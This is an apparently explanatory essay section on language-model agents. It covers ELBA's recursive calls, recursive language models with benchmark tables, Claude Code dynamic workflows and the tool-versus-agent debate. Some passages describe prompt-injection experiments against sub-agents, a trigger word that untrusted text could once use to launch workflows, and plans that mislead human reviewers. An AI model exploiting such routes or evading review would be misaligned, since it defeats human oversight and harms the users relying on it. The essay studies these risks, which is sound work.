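The number of possible outcomes also depends on whether one counts sequences of tools or the texts a program can send. There are about 10⁹⁸⁹ possible 500-character emails that use only the 95 printable characters on an English keyboard. The calendar program from the first section sends an email like this to John Doe. It has only one path and one recipient, but it has far more possible outcomes than the switch program has sequences of tools.

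| Program | Paths | Worst case |
|---|---|---|
| Three yes/no calls, one deciding whether to delete the customer database | 8 | The database is gone |
| Calendar program | 1 | One email to John Doe with any content |
| Refund program | About 1.1 × 10¹⁵ | 50 refunds of $50 |
| Switch program | About 1.1 × 10²⁰, ignoring arguments | Anything ten tools can do in 20 turns |

Program length is no better as a measure. Piet and colleagues observe that a compiled program grows with the task's logic, not with the number of possible outcomes, so the planner doesn't have to write out a tree of them. That makes compiled programs practical, but it also means a dozen lines can contain an entire agent. A reviewer would do better to list the actions a stranger's text could trigger and the arguments it could set.

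### From program generator to agent loop

An agent loop can also arise in a system that starts without one. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) presents ELBA, a system in which a developer's program can call a function named `agent`. The function takes a prompt and a library of permitted functions. It prompts a language model to write a complete program in Haskell, a programming language with strict types, then checks and runs that program. The model writes the whole program in one go and receives none of the results.

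The exception is that the generated program may itself call `agent`. Zhou and colleagues illustrate this with an assistant that compiles bibliographies, for which the model might write something like this:

```
p1 :: BibIO ()
p1 = do
  papers <- dblpSearch "differential privacy"
  if null papers then return ()
  else do
    entry <- dblpFetchBib (head papers)
    let prompt = instructions ++ "Top result: " ++ show entry
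    agent bibLib prompt
```

The first line gives the program's type, which restricts the program to bibliography operations (a later section covers what such types guarantee). The program searches DBLP, a database of computer science papers, for "differential privacy" and stores the identifiers of the matching papers in `papers`. If there are none, it stops. Otherwise it fetches the full entry for the first paper and stores it in `entry`.

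The `let` line builds a new prompt, using `show` to turn the entry into text and `++` to join it to the instructions. The last line passes this prompt and the same library of functions to `agent`. The model reads the search result and writes a second program, which might try better keywords or save some entries to a file. The second program can also end with a call to `agent`, and so can the third.

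The last line of `p1` makes it the first turn of an agent loop, although the text of `p1` never changes and contains no `while`. Without that line, `p1` would be an ordinary fixed plan. If each program copies the record into the next prompt, the model chooses pₜ₊₁ based on (q, p₁, o₁, …, pₜ, oₜ), where q is the user's request, pₜ is the program at turn t, and oₜ is the observation from running that program. This is ReAct's policy with whole programs in place of single actions.

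In ELBA, unlike in ReAct, no outside software keeps the record. Each new call sees only the text that the previous program passed to it, so later turns lose anything that program left out. Under ELBA's instructions, the model must also make some progress before delegating, and must not write a program that simply hands the whole problem to another call.

Zhou and colleagues limit the recursion by giving each call a depth. A call of depth n + 1 can produce a program whose own calls have depth n at most, and a call of depth 0 returns nothing. If every program makes ten calls, a starting depth of 3 allows 1 + 10 + 100 = 111 programs. But the depth doesn't limit how many calls one program makes, since a program can put a call inside a loop. The switch program never nests one call inside another, so a depth limit alone wouldn't rule it out.

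Zhou and colleagues compared ELBA with CaMeL, a system that writes a single program at the start. They used Slack tasks from AgentDojo, a benchmark that also tests resistance to prompt injection. With both systems' security policies switched off and no attacks, ELBA completed 64 of 84 runs across four models and CaMeL completed 61, so ELBA's extra flexibility made little difference on ordinary tasks. The gap was wider when the data contained injected instructions (81% for ELBA against 69% for CaMeL). ELBA took about three times as long on AgentDojo overall, mainly because it calls the model again in response to data.

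The recursion also lets hostile text reach a model that can act on it. All four models resisted all of AgentDojo's standard attacks, even without policies. To test what would happen if a model failed to resist, Zhou and colleagues altered ELBA so that a sub-agent whose data contained an injection received only that data as its prompt. With the policies still off, between 16% and 42% of the injections succeeded, depending on the model. The test is deliberately pessimistic because it assumes that every injection fools the sub-agent that reads it.

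Piet and colleagues would forbid programs like `p1` because the model's output selects the next action. Zhou and colleagues allow the feedback, selection and repetition but limit what the program can do. The bibliography assistant can save only entries that came from DBLP, however many times it calls itself.

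## Programs in which a model calls itself: recursive language models

ELBA's generated programs call the model again to get more programs. A *recursive language model*, the design behind DSPy's `RLM` module, uses a similar mechanism to answer questions about texts too long for a model to read. The idea first appeared in a 2025 blog post. *Recursive Language Models* (Zhang, Kraska and Khattab, 2025) reported fuller experiments that December and was revised in May 2026.

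A language model can take in only so much text at once, a limit called its *context window*. GPT-5, the OpenAI model used in most of the paper's tests, has a window of 272,000 tokens, and its answers get worse well before the window is full. The usual remedy is to have a model summarize the older material whenever space runs out. Summarizing works badly when the answer depends on nearly every line, because a summary has to leave most lines out.

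### How the method works

A recursive language model keeps the long text out of the window. Software stores the text as a variable in a Python interpreter, and the *root model* receives the question, the length of the text and perhaps its opening lines. The root writes some code, the interpreter runs it, and the root sees the beginning of whatever the code printed. This repeats until the code puts an answer in a designated variable. Slightly simplified, the method is:

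```
state = start_interpreter(context=long_text)
history = [question, describe(long_text)]
while "Final" not in state:
    code = model(history)
    output = run(code, state)
    history += [code, describe(output)]
return state["Final"]
```

Here `describe` gives only the length of a text and its first few lines. The interpreter keeps its variables between turns. It also provides the root with a function, `llm_query`, that sends a prompt to a model and returns the reply.

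Suppose the shop owner has 40,000 old customer messages, about six million tokens, and asks which product most often arrives broken. The root might first print the opening of the file to see how the messages are separated. Then it might write this:

```
messages = context.split("\n---\n")
products = []
for m in messages:
    products.append(llm_query(
        "Which product arrived broken? Give its name, or 'none'.\n" + m))
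print(products[:5])
```

The five printed answers show the root whether the question worked. If they look right, it can finish in the next turn:

```
from collections import Counter
counts = Counter(p for p in products if p != "none")
Final = counts.most_common(1)[0][0]
```

The root has read perhaps a page of the file. Separate model calls read the messages, and ordinary Python did the counting.

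A real run would probably use fewer calls, because Zhang and colleagues tell the root model that each call can hold around 500,000 characters. About 50 calls would then cover the whole file, but each would have to process a very long text, which the method was meant to avoid.

Cutting off the printed output forces the root to keep long results in variables and limits how fast its history grows. If each turn adds at most c tokens and the window holds K, the root has at most K/c turns, or 272 turns for GPT-5 with c = 1,000. A single turn can still launch any number of calls. The final answer is also read from a variable, so it can be longer than the model could write in one reply.

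### Calls inside code

Agents could already hand work to sub-agents, but in many systems the model has to write out every delegation. At 20 tokens per request, delegating 40,000 messages one at a time would take 800,000 tokens, about three times GPT-5's context window, not counting the messages themselves. The loop above takes well under a hundred tokens whether there are 40 messages or 40,000. A nested loop could make a call for every pair of messages, which would be too many calls for any model to write out individually.

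Zhang and colleagues think this may be the most important part of the design, but their experiments don't isolate it. The closest comparison is with an agent that could also call a model from its code but received the text directly in its context window. On OOLONG-Pairs, that agent scored 28.4 and the recursive model scored 58.0. The agent was instructed to copy any data it needed into its code, so the gap probably comes more from storing the text as a variable than from this part of the design.

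### What the depths mean

The recursion depth is how many levels of model calls are allowed below the root. At depth 0, the root can use the interpreter but can't call a model. At depth 1, its code can call a model with `llm_query`, as in the example.

Depth 2 adds another function, `rlm_query`, which starts a complete recursive language model on a piece of the text. The new system has its own interpreter and loop, and its code can use `llm_query`. At depth 3, these inner systems can start one more layer of the same kind. When a program calls `rlm_query` at the maximum depth, the call runs as a plain `llm_query` instead.

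Going from depth 1 to depth 2 therefore changes the kind of call as well as the number of levels. An `llm_query` call is a language-model function, while an `rlm_query` call is a sub-agent whose only tool is an interpreter.

### Results with GPT-5

Zhang and colleagues used GPT-5 as the root model and sent its calls to the cheaper GPT-5-mini, so the model wasn't literally calling itself. The table gives scores out of 100, with the average cost per question in brackets.

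| | OOLONG-Pairs | OOLONG | CodeQA | BrowseComp-Plus |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5 alone | 0.1 ($0.16) | 44.0 ($0.14) | 24.0 ($0.13) | 0.0 (text too long) |
| Depth 0 | 43.9 ($0.69) | 36.0 ($0.37) | 58.0 ($0.18) | 88.0 ($0.44) |
| Depth 1 | 58.0 ($0.33) | 56.0 ($0.43) | 62.0 ($0.11) | 91.3 ($0.99) |
| Depth 2 | 65.5 ($0.33) | 56.5 ($1.10) | 66.0 ($0.15) | 92.0 ($0.55) |
| Depth 3 | 76.0 ($0.39) | 58.0 ($0.51) | 58.0 ($0.15) | 92.0 ($0.51) |

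The most striking results are in the OOLONG-Pairs column, where GPT-5 alone got almost nothing right even though the text is only 32,000 tokens long and fits easily in its window. The text is a list of questions that users asked. Each question belongs to one of six categories, such as location or numeric value, but the text doesn't state which one. A typical task is to list every pair of users who both asked at least one question about a location or a number.

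The largest improvement comes at depth 0, where the root can't yet call a model. Once a program has assigned the categories, a few lines of Python can compare every pair of users without missing any, even when there are thousands of pairs. Model calls help assign the categories. Without them, the root has to infer the categories from keywords, much as a keyword search would have handled the refund messages.

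OOLONG uses the same kind of data but asks for a single overall answer, and it gives the best evidence that the calls matter. At depth 0, the system scored 36.0, below the 44.0 that GPT-5 scored by reading the text directly. One level of calls raised the system's score to 56.0, and two more levels added only two points.

CodeQA consists of multiple-choice questions about collections of program code. The scores rise to 66 at depth 2 and fall back to 58 at depth 3. All the scores differ by multiples of two points, which fits a test of 50 questions. The fall would then be a difference of four questions and might well be chance.

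The answer to each BrowseComp-Plus question draws on several of 1,000 documents. Recursion depth makes little difference on this test, because the root model can use code to search for promising documents and have a model read only those. Zhang and colleagues estimate that having GPT-5-mini read all the documents would cost $1.50 to $2.75 per question. OpenCode, a coding agent, scored 94.0 on the same test with GPT-5 and the documents in a file, slightly better than any of the recursive systems, but only 4.8 on OOLONG-Pairs.

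The average costs hide some expensive runs. On OOLONG at depth 2, the standard deviation was $3.25 around an average of $1.10. Zhang and colleagues found that the median run cost less than asking GPT-5 directly, while a few runs that struggled to find an answer pushed up the average. (They also print identical averages and standard deviations for OOLONG and BrowseComp-Plus at depth 3, so one of those entries may be a copying error.)

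How the root divides up the work can matter more than the depth of recursion. Zhang and colleagues tested the newer GPT-5.2 on LongCoT-mini, a set of long reasoning problems. The model scored 38.7 alone and 50.6 as the root of a depth-1 system, but its score on the mathematics problems fell from 26.0 to 5.6. They then gave the root detailed instructions to list the subproblems and their dependencies, solve them in order through model calls, check each answer, and do no mathematics itself. The overall score rose to 65.6 and the mathematics score to 32.0. People wrote those instructions, and so had in effect written much of the plan.

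### A reproduction with open models

*Think, But Don't Overthink* (Wang, 2026) repeated part of the study with two openly available models, DeepSeek v3.2 and Kimi K2, and found that depth 2 usually lowered accuracy. The simpler of the two tests, S-NIAH, hides one phrase or number in a long irrelevant text. Both models found it every time when they read the text directly. DeepSeek's accuracy fell to 85% at depth 1 and 70% at depth 2, while Kimi's fell to 90% at both depths.

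The systems also became much slower. On S-NIAH, DeepSeek on its own averaged 3.6 seconds per question, compared with 89.3 seconds at depth 1 and 344.5 seconds at depth 2. At depth 2, it spent 741.5 seconds on an OOLONG question that asked only whether one category was more common than another, and it produced a long step-by-step essay instead of an answer in the required form.

The two studies disagree less than their titles suggest. On OOLONG, which both used, the results are:

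| Model | Alone | Depth 1 | Depth 2 |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5 (Zhang and colleagues) | 44.0 | 56.0 | 56.5 |
| Qwen3-Coder (Zhang and colleagues) | 36.0 | 48.0 | 26.0 |
| DeepSeek v3.2 (Wang) | 0.0 | 42.1 | 33.7 |
| Kimi K2 (Wang) | 86.6 | 60.0 | 55.0 |

The second level of recursion barely helped GPT-5 on this test either. GPT-5's large gains from depth came on OOLONG-Pairs, which Wang didn't run. Wang also ran each condition only once, with 20 questions, so each question is worth five points. Kimi's drop from depth 1 to depth 2 equals one question, and DeepSeek's equals fewer than two. DeepSeek's 30-point drop on S-NIAH, from no recursion to depth 2, is harder to attribute to chance.

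Some of the difference probably comes from how well the models write code. Qwen3-Coder, the open model in the original study, also did much worse on OOLONG at depth 2. Zhang and colleagues blame syntax errors, which Qwen3-Coder made far more often than GPT-5 and which the nested systems repeated. Wang saw related mistakes, such as Kimi returning a Python `print` statement instead of the answer it would have printed. But syntax errors can't explain everything, because Qwen3-Coder's score on BrowseComp-Plus rose from 44.7 to 68.0 at depth 2.

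The length of the texts also matters. Wang's OOLONG texts ranged from 1,024 to 65,536 tokens, while the original scores came from texts of about 131,000 tokens. Zhang and colleagues found that recursion consistently beat GPT-5 alone only above roughly 16,000 tokens. A model that can read a short text without trouble, as Kimi evidently could, gains nothing from splitting it up and has more chances to make mistakes.

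Wang's strongest result in favor of recursion, DeepSeek's rise from 0.0 to 42.1, is also weaker than it looks, because much of the rise may reflect better formatting. Wang explains in the notes that DeepSeek had found the answers on its own but wrapped them in long explanations that the scoring program rejected.

Both studies measured waiting times with model calls running one after another. The slowest query that Wang describes took 1,223.6 seconds at depth 1, so the second level of recursion isn't the only cause of long waits.

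There is fairly good evidence that one level of calls helps with long texts, provided the root model writes code well. The evidence for second and third levels rests mainly on one model and the 20 queries of OOLONG-Pairs, Zhang and colleagues' own test. The models in these depth comparisons all date from 2025, and newer ones might make fewer of the mistakes that spoiled the deeper runs.

### Cost and termination

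Two theory papers give reasons to expect that recursion could help, though both study models that write out each call as text instead of placing it in code. In *Recursive Models for Long-Horizon Reasoning*, Yang, Srebro and Li (2026) prove that if each call can hold on the order of S tokens, deep enough recursion can solve any problem that takes up to 2^O(S) steps. A model working in one continuous text would need an exponentially longer window. One level of calls can solve as much as the best possible method that stays within a single context, such as repeated summarization, and deeper recursion can solve more. However, the recursion in the proof may need exponentially many levels, and each call must still have room for the input it reads. In *Recursive Language Models Generalize Out of Domain*, Yang, Li and colleagues (2026) ask whether isolated contexts also help a model learn. With enough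 training data, a model that sees the full record does as well as one with isolated contexts on problems like those in training. On longer problems it fails because it has learned shortcuts from text outside the current subproblem, while the model with isolated contexts stays accurate.

In practice, the number of calls becomes a problem long before exponential depth. If every system makes 20 calls, the lowest level has 20 calls at depth 1, 400 at depth 2 and 8,000 at depth 3. At depth 3, the 421 systems above the lowest level (1 + 20 + 400) also each run a loop. With ten turns per loop, they call a model another 4,210 times to write code. At three seconds per call, one after another, all 12,210 calls would take more than ten hours.

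More generally, if each system has at most t turns and makes at most b calls in total, then a system of depth d calls a model at most

t(1 + b + b² + … + bᵈ⁻¹) + bᵈ

times. GPT-5 evidently came nowhere near such numbers, since its OOLONG-Pairs runs at depth 3 cost 39 cents on average, only six cents more than at depth 1. The depth is a ceiling, and a root that is allowed three levels may use only one.

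A depth limit alone doesn't guarantee that a run ends, because it doesn't limit t or b. The code between calls can also run forever. Guaranteeing that a run ends requires limits on turns and total calls, and a time limit on the code.

In one of their training experiments, Zhang and colleagues limited the root to 20 turns of at most 4,096 tokens each. Qwen3-Coder had made thousands of calls for basic tasks, so they added a paragraph to its prompt asking it to process several lines per call, for example by making 200 calls for 1,000 lines instead of 1,000 calls. A model can fail to follow such an instruction, and they list runaway call costs among the problems they leave for future work.

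*Recursive Language Models (RLMs)*, the documentation for their software package, describes another control, `max_concurrent_subcalls`, which limits how many nested systems run in parallel. This keeps a large batch from starting all at once but doesn't limit the batch's size. One of the package's interpreters can also stop code that runs too long.

### Sub-agents in coding tools

Model-written scripts also start sub-agents in coding tools, where a call can change files as well as return text. The dynamic workflows in Claude Code, introduced in the previous section, work much like a recursive language model. The script keeps the sub-agents' results in its own variables, and according to Anthropic, only the final answer enters the main conversation. A script can assign different models to different sub-agents, much as Zhang and colleagues paired GPT-5 with GPT-5-mini.

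The important difference is that each `agent()` call starts a sub-agent with tools. The call corresponds to `rlm_query`, not `llm_query`, and the sub-agent's tools can access more than an interpreter that holds one document can.

According to Inventive HQ, a technology site that described the feature during its research preview, Claude Code allows at most 16 agents at once and 1,000 in total per run, with the total capped to stop a runaway loop. *Ingest*, a summary of Anthropic's documentation, gives the same figures. Both limits apply to the number of agents, not the levels of nesting.

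A cap on the total number of calls is a good substitute for a depth limit, because it applies however the calls are arranged. If the main program and each call it leads to make 20 further calls, a cap of 1,000 could let the recursion complete its first two levels (420 calls) and would stop it 580 calls into the third. The same cap would stop a flat loop that makes one call for each of 40,000 messages at message 1,000, whereas a depth limit of 1 would let the loop finish.

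Users can relax some of Claude Code's other safeguards with a setting called ultracode, which has Claude plan a workflow for every substantial task. According to Anthropic, the setting also removes the warning about large workflows and lifts the limit on how many sub-agents Claude can run at once when it starts them directly, outside a script.

#### How fixed a workflow is

In *ultracode and Dynamic Workflows*, the commentator laiso argues that only the writing of a workflow is dynamic. Anthropic makes a script return an error if it tries to read the current time or generate a random number, so that a relaunched run repeats the same `agent()` calls. When a user stops and relaunches a run, sub-agents that had finished return their saved results, up to the first one whose prompt has changed. That sub-agent and all later ones run again.

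The script can still pass on text that nobody reviewed. In the example from the previous section, one sub-agent's list of file names became part of other sub-agents' instructions. Claude Code partly addresses this in auto mode, where a classifier reviews actions in place of the user. Claude Code marks prompts from a script as computed text, so the classifier doesn't treat them as requests from the user.

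A user can request a workflow by typing "ultracode" in a prompt. Until version 2.1.210, untrusted text could also start one if it contained the word, such as a comment on a code change that other software relayed into the conversation. Now the word works only in text that the user types.

Before a workflow runs, Claude Code shows a prompt that lists the planned phases and offers to display the script. In auto mode, it shows this prompt only before the first launch, and if ultracode is also on, it never shows it.

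### The Bun port

In May 2026, Jarred Sumner used dynamic workflows to translate Bun, a widely used program for running JavaScript, from the language Zig to Rust. *Rewriting Bun in Rust* (Sumner, 2026) describes about 50 workflows running over 11 days on a codebase of 535,496 lines. Sumner works for Anthropic, which bought Bun in December 2025, and he used a pre-release version of one of its models, so his account isn't an independent test.

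The workflows were almost certainly model-written scripts that start sub-agents. Anthropic's documentation uses "dynamic workflow" to mean such a script, and Sumner describes asking Claude to edit the loops, though he prints only a short one, labeled as pseudocode. For each file in his trial run, one sub-agent wrote the Rust version, two others looked for mistakes, and a fourth applied the corrections. The reviewers worked in separate contexts and saw only the changed code.

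This structure is wide but apparently shallow. Sumner eventually ran four workflows side by side with 16 sub-agents each, which matches the reported limit. Bun had 1,448 Zig files, so at four sub-agents per file, the translation step alone would need 5,792 sub-agents, or at least six runs under a cap of 1,000.

Two minutes into the first full attempt, the sub-agents began undoing each other's work. They shared one copy of the code, and some used commands that set aside or discarded every uncommitted change in it. Sumner had Claude add an instruction to the workflow that sub-agents must never use those commands, and the work resumed. The instruction was written in English, like the $50 limit in the sub-agent version of the refund program.

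Each script may well have been a fixed plan while it ran, but the project as a whole was not, because for most of the 11 days Sumner watched the results and had Claude rewrite the scripts when something went wrong. This served the same purpose as re-invoking a planner.

### What the calls can act on

A recursive language model contains an agent loop at every depth. The root meets three of the four conditions from the previous section: feedback, selection and repetition. The fourth, range, depends on the interpreter.

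A recursive language model working on a static document in a sealed interpreter can take only a few kinds of action. The `llm_query` calls return strings, and the root can only compute, make more calls and give an answer. A hostile customer message could still be worded so that it is miscounted. If the root prints the model's reply to that message, the reply could also influence the next piece of code the root writes. The owner might then get the wrong answer or a very large bill, but the program cannot send an email or pay a refund.

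By default, the package runs the root's code without isolation, on the user's own machine and in the same process as the rest of the software. *Recursive Language Models (RLMs)* describes this as reasonable for low-risk work such as simple benchmarks, but warns of problems if malicious users can influence the prompts. For those cases, the package offers isolated interpreters on separate machines.

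The package also lets developers add their own tools to the interpreter. If the shop owner's developer added a `refund` tool, the root could write a loop that reads all 40,000 old messages and refunds their senders, and the recursion depth would still be 1.

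## Does calling a model again make a plan goal-directed?

A program can have the structure of an agent loop without pursuing a goal. If the switch program rolled a die to pick each tool, it would still act, record the result and act again for 20 turns, but it wouldn't be trying to achieve anything. Conversely, a planner that tested thousands of programs in simulation and kept whichever one moved the most money would be pursuing an outcome, even if the winning program was a plain list of payments with no model calls.

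Roughly, a system is *goal-directed* if it takes actions because of their likely outcomes. A program's structure determines what it can do, and any goal it has affects which of those things it does and whether it looks for a way around an obstacle.

### Tools, agents and services

The dispute over whether a planning system must be an agent is older than language-model planners. In 2012 Holden Karnofsky, a co-founder of the charity evaluator GiveWell, criticized the Singularity Institute, an AI safety group, for neglecting the difference between a tool and an agent. Karnofsky (2012) uses Google Maps as his example of a tool in a passage reposted as *Holden Karnofsky's Singularity Institute Objection 2*. Google Maps scores possible routes and displays the best one, and the driver decides whether to take it.

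In his account, both kinds of system start by calculating which action would score highest on some measure, given a fixed set of data. They differ in the last line:

```
best = max(possible_actions, key=lambda a: score(predict(a, data)))
report(best)       # a tool
execute(best)      # an agent
```

Karnofsky calls it a category error to describe the tool version as wanting anything, and he sees no reason to expect deception from it. He would let a tool collect more data only through a small set of safe actions chosen in advance, and would widen that set as people gained experience. The refund sub-agent that kept only its two look-up tools is close to what he describes.

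By this standard, a planner whose plans run without further choice is a tool if a person reviews each plan first and an agent if nobody does. A shop owner who reads the four-line refund program before starting it is using the planner as a tool. If her software starts every program automatically, the same planner is an agent. The embedded calls make little difference here, because each one answers a question about a message and none calculates a best action.

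Some bad plans are easy to reject. *Tools versus agents*, a reply to Karnofsky, gives the example of a system that has to prevent human suffering and proposes killing everyone. In *Reply to Holden on 'Tool AI'*, Yudkowsky (2012) is more concerned with plans whose faults a reader can't see. A system might recommend a DNA sequence for a protein that cures cancer, and no human could check that the protein would fold as predicted.

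Requiring the plan to be understandable creates another problem, because the system must predict how the reader will react, and its search can exploit that reaction. Yudkowsky borrows an example from a commenter in which a patient asks for the cheapest way to get rid of a disease. The system replies that death is certain and near, and the patient ends their life, which gets rid of the disease at no cost.

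Yudkowsky also disputes Karnofsky's claim that nearly all software works as a tool. Cars adjust their fuel mix and trading programs place orders without human approval. But these examples also suggest that executing actions isn't enough to make software an agent in any worrying sense, since a fuel controller acts all day without searching for new ways to achieve a goal.

He doesn't dismiss human approval, but he thinks somebody has to work out exactly what it achieves, and admits that he hadn't got far with this. The answer is fairly simple for the refund program, where the owner can confirm that she will lose at most $2,500. Her approval would achieve much less if the plan contained steps she couldn't evaluate.

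In *Why Tool AIs Want to Be Agent AIs* (2016), Gwern argues that people will replace tools with agents even if tools are safer. If human review takes half the time of each decision, no improvement to the AI can more than double the speed, so a better AI makes it more tempting to remove the reviewer. People who trust a tool also stop checking its answers. Gwern reports that from around 2007, human mistakes increasingly decided games of "advanced chess", where people play with computer help. Some of these mistakes were as trivial as clicking the wrong square.

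Gwern also argues that agents are more capable than tools. An agent can choose to do nothing except answer questions, so it should perform at least as well as a tool, provided it has enough data to learn when acting doesn't help. It can also choose which data to collect and how long to work on a problem. Much of the evidence comes from statistics, where methods that adapt to incoming data often beat those that don't. A trial that stops once the result is clear may need only a fraction of the observations that a fixed-size trial would. Similarly, joining the shorter of two randomly chosen queues greatly reduces the longest expected wait compared with joining one at random, and looking at a third queue adds little.

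These examples are good evidence against open-loop plans but much weaker evidence against fixed plans with branches. A statistician can write a trial's stopping rule before the first patient arrives, and a programmer can write "join the shorter queue" in one line of code. The plan needs a model at runtime only when nobody can write the rule in advance, as when customers describe broken mugs in many different ways.

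In *Reframing Superintelligence*, Drexler (2019) treats planning as a service. He expects advanced AI to consist of many systems that each perform a task with limits on its scope, time and resources. In his example of engineering design, one component turns a client's wishes into a specification, while others propose, simulate and score designs. Designs that pass screening can go into use. No component has the task of improving itself or bringing about a preferred state of the world. Drexler also expects development to remove activity that doesn't serve the task, because such activity wastes resources.

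He comes closest to describing a fixed plan with branches. He argues that people can approve a strategy slowly and still include very fast responses in it. US nuclear strategy took decades to plan and revise, yet it allows for an immediate counterstrike. A fast response therefore doesn't require handing strategic decisions to a machine. Approval in advance also has limits, since one false reading at the counterstrike branch could start a nuclear war.

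### Two tests of agency

Kenton, Kumar and colleagues (2022), in *Discovering Agents*, define an agent as a system that would adapt its policy if its actions had different effects. Their simplest example is a mouse in the middle of three squares, which can go left or right. The floor is icy, so the mouse ends up on the side it chose with probability 0.75 and on the other side otherwise. The cheese is on the right with probability 0.9. The chances of getting it are:

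- going right: 0.75 × 0.9 + 0.25 × 0.1 = 0.70
- going left: 0.25 × 0.9 + 0.75 × 0.1 = 0.30

If somebody changes the probability that the cheese is on the right from 0.9 to 0.1, the two results swap, and a mouse that learns of the change will go left. But a rock that happens to be the right size to block a pipe would stay the same size if the pipe were wider, so Kenton and colleagues don't count it as an agent.

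A causal graph with two layers formalizes this. One layer contains the mouse's choice, its position and whether it gets the cheese. The other contains a mechanism for each of these: the mouse's decision rule, the slipperiness of the ice and the location of the cheese. The mouse is an agent because changing the ice or the cheese's location changes its decision rule. Pushing the mouse to the left in a single trial wouldn't test this, because the mouse would have no chance to adapt to the push.

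The answer can depend on where you draw the system's boundary. Suppose somebody rewires a heater so that it cools the room. The thermostat keeps switching it on as the room gets colder, so the thermostat alone is not an agent. But designers who knew about the rewiring would have built a different thermostat, so the thermostat together with its design process is an agent. Similarly, Kenton and colleagues say that the process of training a policy by reinforcement learning would respond to a change in what actions do, while the finished policy generally wouldn't.

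A language model's weights also stay fixed during use, but its choices can still depend on what it reads about their consequences. A ReAct agent that sees a "save" button delete a draft can stop pressing the button without retraining. Whether an embedded call passes the test therefore depends partly on what its input shows about the effects of its answers.

Engineers usually draw the line elsewhere. Anthropic's *Building effective agents* (2024) distinguishes workflows, in which predefined code determines the path, from agents, in which models direct their own steps and tool use. One of its example workflows sorts customer messages and sends refund requests to a separate process. It also counts a design as a workflow when a central model chooses the subtasks and delegates them to other models. The central model has much of what an earlier section called selection, so the category of workflows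 is broad.

In *Building effective agents*, a post recommending Anthropic's article, Willison complains that most people who use the word "agent" assume everyone shares their definition. Anthropic's article distinguished agents by who directs the steps. Its later guide, *Building Effective AI Agents*, adds that agents keep working toward completing a goal.

The two tests can give different results. Yao and colleagues saw ReAct agents get stuck repeating themselves. A stuck agent still directs its own steps, so it is an agent in Anthropic's sense. But it fails Kenton and colleagues' test while it is stuck, because it isn't adapting to the effects of those steps.

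### How embedded calls might bring goals back

The case for saying that embedded calls make a plan goal-directed rests on four premises:

1. The call responds to the results of earlier actions.
2. Its prompt contains the goal.
3. It has authority to act.
4. It persists over many steps.

The argument's conclusion is that a plan containing such a call pursues the goal while it runs, even though the plan's text is fixed. But each premise is true of only some embedded calls.

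#### Responding to results

A thermostat responds to the results of its actions, but it isn't an agent by itself. The call in the refund program doesn't even respond to results, since it never receives the result of a refund.

A model that is given the history can do more than a thermostat. Suppose the owner's payment provider starts rejecting refunds above $40. A call whose input includes the error might split a $50 refund into payments of $40 and $10, reaching the same outcome by a new route. But a planner could have written that response into the program in advance, so one such recovery is weak evidence of a goal. The evidence would be stronger if someone blocked the refund in several unexpected ways and the system kept finding other routes to it.

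#### The goal in the prompt

*Beyond AI as Assistants* (2026), a paper on automated research in cosmology, includes the goal explicitly when it defines an agent's policy:

aₜ ~ π(· | G, T, Cₜ₋₁)

As in ReAct's policy, the action depends on the context so far, but this formula also has explicit terms for the goal G and the set of available tools T.

An input can function as a goal if the system's choices consistently follow it. One could object that G is just another input, like the destination in Google Maps. Drexler makes a similar point about machine translation, where the system has no goal beyond translating the sentence it receives, however much intelligence that takes. But changing G from "refund customers with broken items" to "pay out as little as possible" would lead a capable model to choose different actions in nearly every situation.

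The refund program's call to the model doesn't include the goal G. It contains only a question about broken items, which the model would also answer for an owner who wanted to refuse those customers. Leaving out the goal isn't a complete safeguard, because a model may guess the purpose of a question. Gwern thought the idea of a tool developing its own plans was mostly theoretical until GPT-3, an OpenAI model trained only to predict text, proved good at imitating agents.

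Adding a sentence to the prompt could also turn the question into a decision. If the prompt said "Answering yes will pay this customer $50", the model might consider whether the customer deserved the money or the shop could afford it. An owner who wants only a classification should probably leave that sentence out.

#### Authority to act

A language-model function can cause actions even though it has no tools, because the program uses its answer without anyone reviewing it first. If the program issues a refund whenever the function answers "yes", then that answer is enough to send the money.

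Drexler offers a different reason not to worry about a system whose output has effects. He argues that what the system is optimized for makes the difference. Let V(a) be the value of plan a if the client follows it, and let P(a, m) be the probability that the client accepts the plan after reading description m. If a rejected plan is worth nothing, there are two ways to score advice:

- by its results: P(a, m) × V(a)
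- by its results if accepted: V(a)

Suppose a plan is worth $1,000 to the shop owner. She would accept it half the time if she knew about a certain risk, and 90% of the time if she didn't. Hiding the risk raises the first score from $500 to $900 but leaves the second at $1,000, so only an advisor optimized for results gains from misleading her.

While a plan runs, the interpreter accepts every valid answer, so P is 1 and the two scores are equal. An embedded call then has nobody to persuade, unless a person or another model reads its answer before the program acts on it. Persuasion is more of a concern earlier, when the planner presents its program for approval. Drexler's argument also depends on how developers train the system, which the owner can't learn by reading the plan. He warns that competition may favor advice that people like over advice that is good for them.

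#### Persistence

Each call in the refund program starts with no memory of the others. Drexler recommends something similar for systems that answer questions, partly because it makes collusion between them harder. But a program can supply the missing memory, as the `exec` program does with its `history` variable, and its loop can then work on one objective for hours.

Persistence gives a program the opportunity to recover from failures and build on earlier steps, but it doesn't imply a goal. Backup software, for example, can run for years without one. A goal doesn't require persistence either, because a single call may be enough to choose an irreversible payment.

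#### How broad the goal is

A ReAct sub-agent with the owner's request, a payment tool and a long history meets all four premises, and it seems reasonable to call it goal-directed. A language-model function that answers one question about one message doesn't meet all four. The argument therefore succeeds for some embedded calls but not all.

Even when calling a model again makes a plan goal-directed, the goal may be modest. People worry about goal-directed AI largely because many goals give a system reasons to protect itself and acquire resources. Drexler points out that these reasons apply to goals of indefinite scope and duration, and that for a limited task such efforts would only waste resources. For example, a system that has to process 50 messages by this evening gains nothing from acquiring a data center.

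A goal can be unlimited even when its topic is narrow. Drexler recalls a remark by the AI pioneer Marvin Minsky that playing the best possible game of chess could justify converting all accessible resources into chess-playing machinery. Similarly, a shop's goal to "keep customers as happy as possible" has no clear end, unlike "refund up to $50 for each broken item in these 50 messages."

### Four programs under the two tests

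| Program | Would it adapt if its actions had different effects? | Workflow or agent? |
|---|---|---|
| Refund program | Not while it runs | Workflow |
| Recursive model reading a static document | Yes, if the root can observe the change | Agent |
| Planner called again only on failure | Only if the change causes a failure | Mostly a workflow |
| Calls that each see one fragment | Not while it runs | Workflow |

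Suppose a fault in the `refund` tool makes it charge customers instead of paying them. The refund program would charge everyone who reported a broken item, because it doesn't check where the money goes. A planner that knew about the fault would have written a different program. As with the thermostat, the program alone fails the test that Kenton and colleagues propose, but the program and its planner together pass. The shop owner's goal shaped the plan before the plan ran and doesn't influence the model's answers after that.

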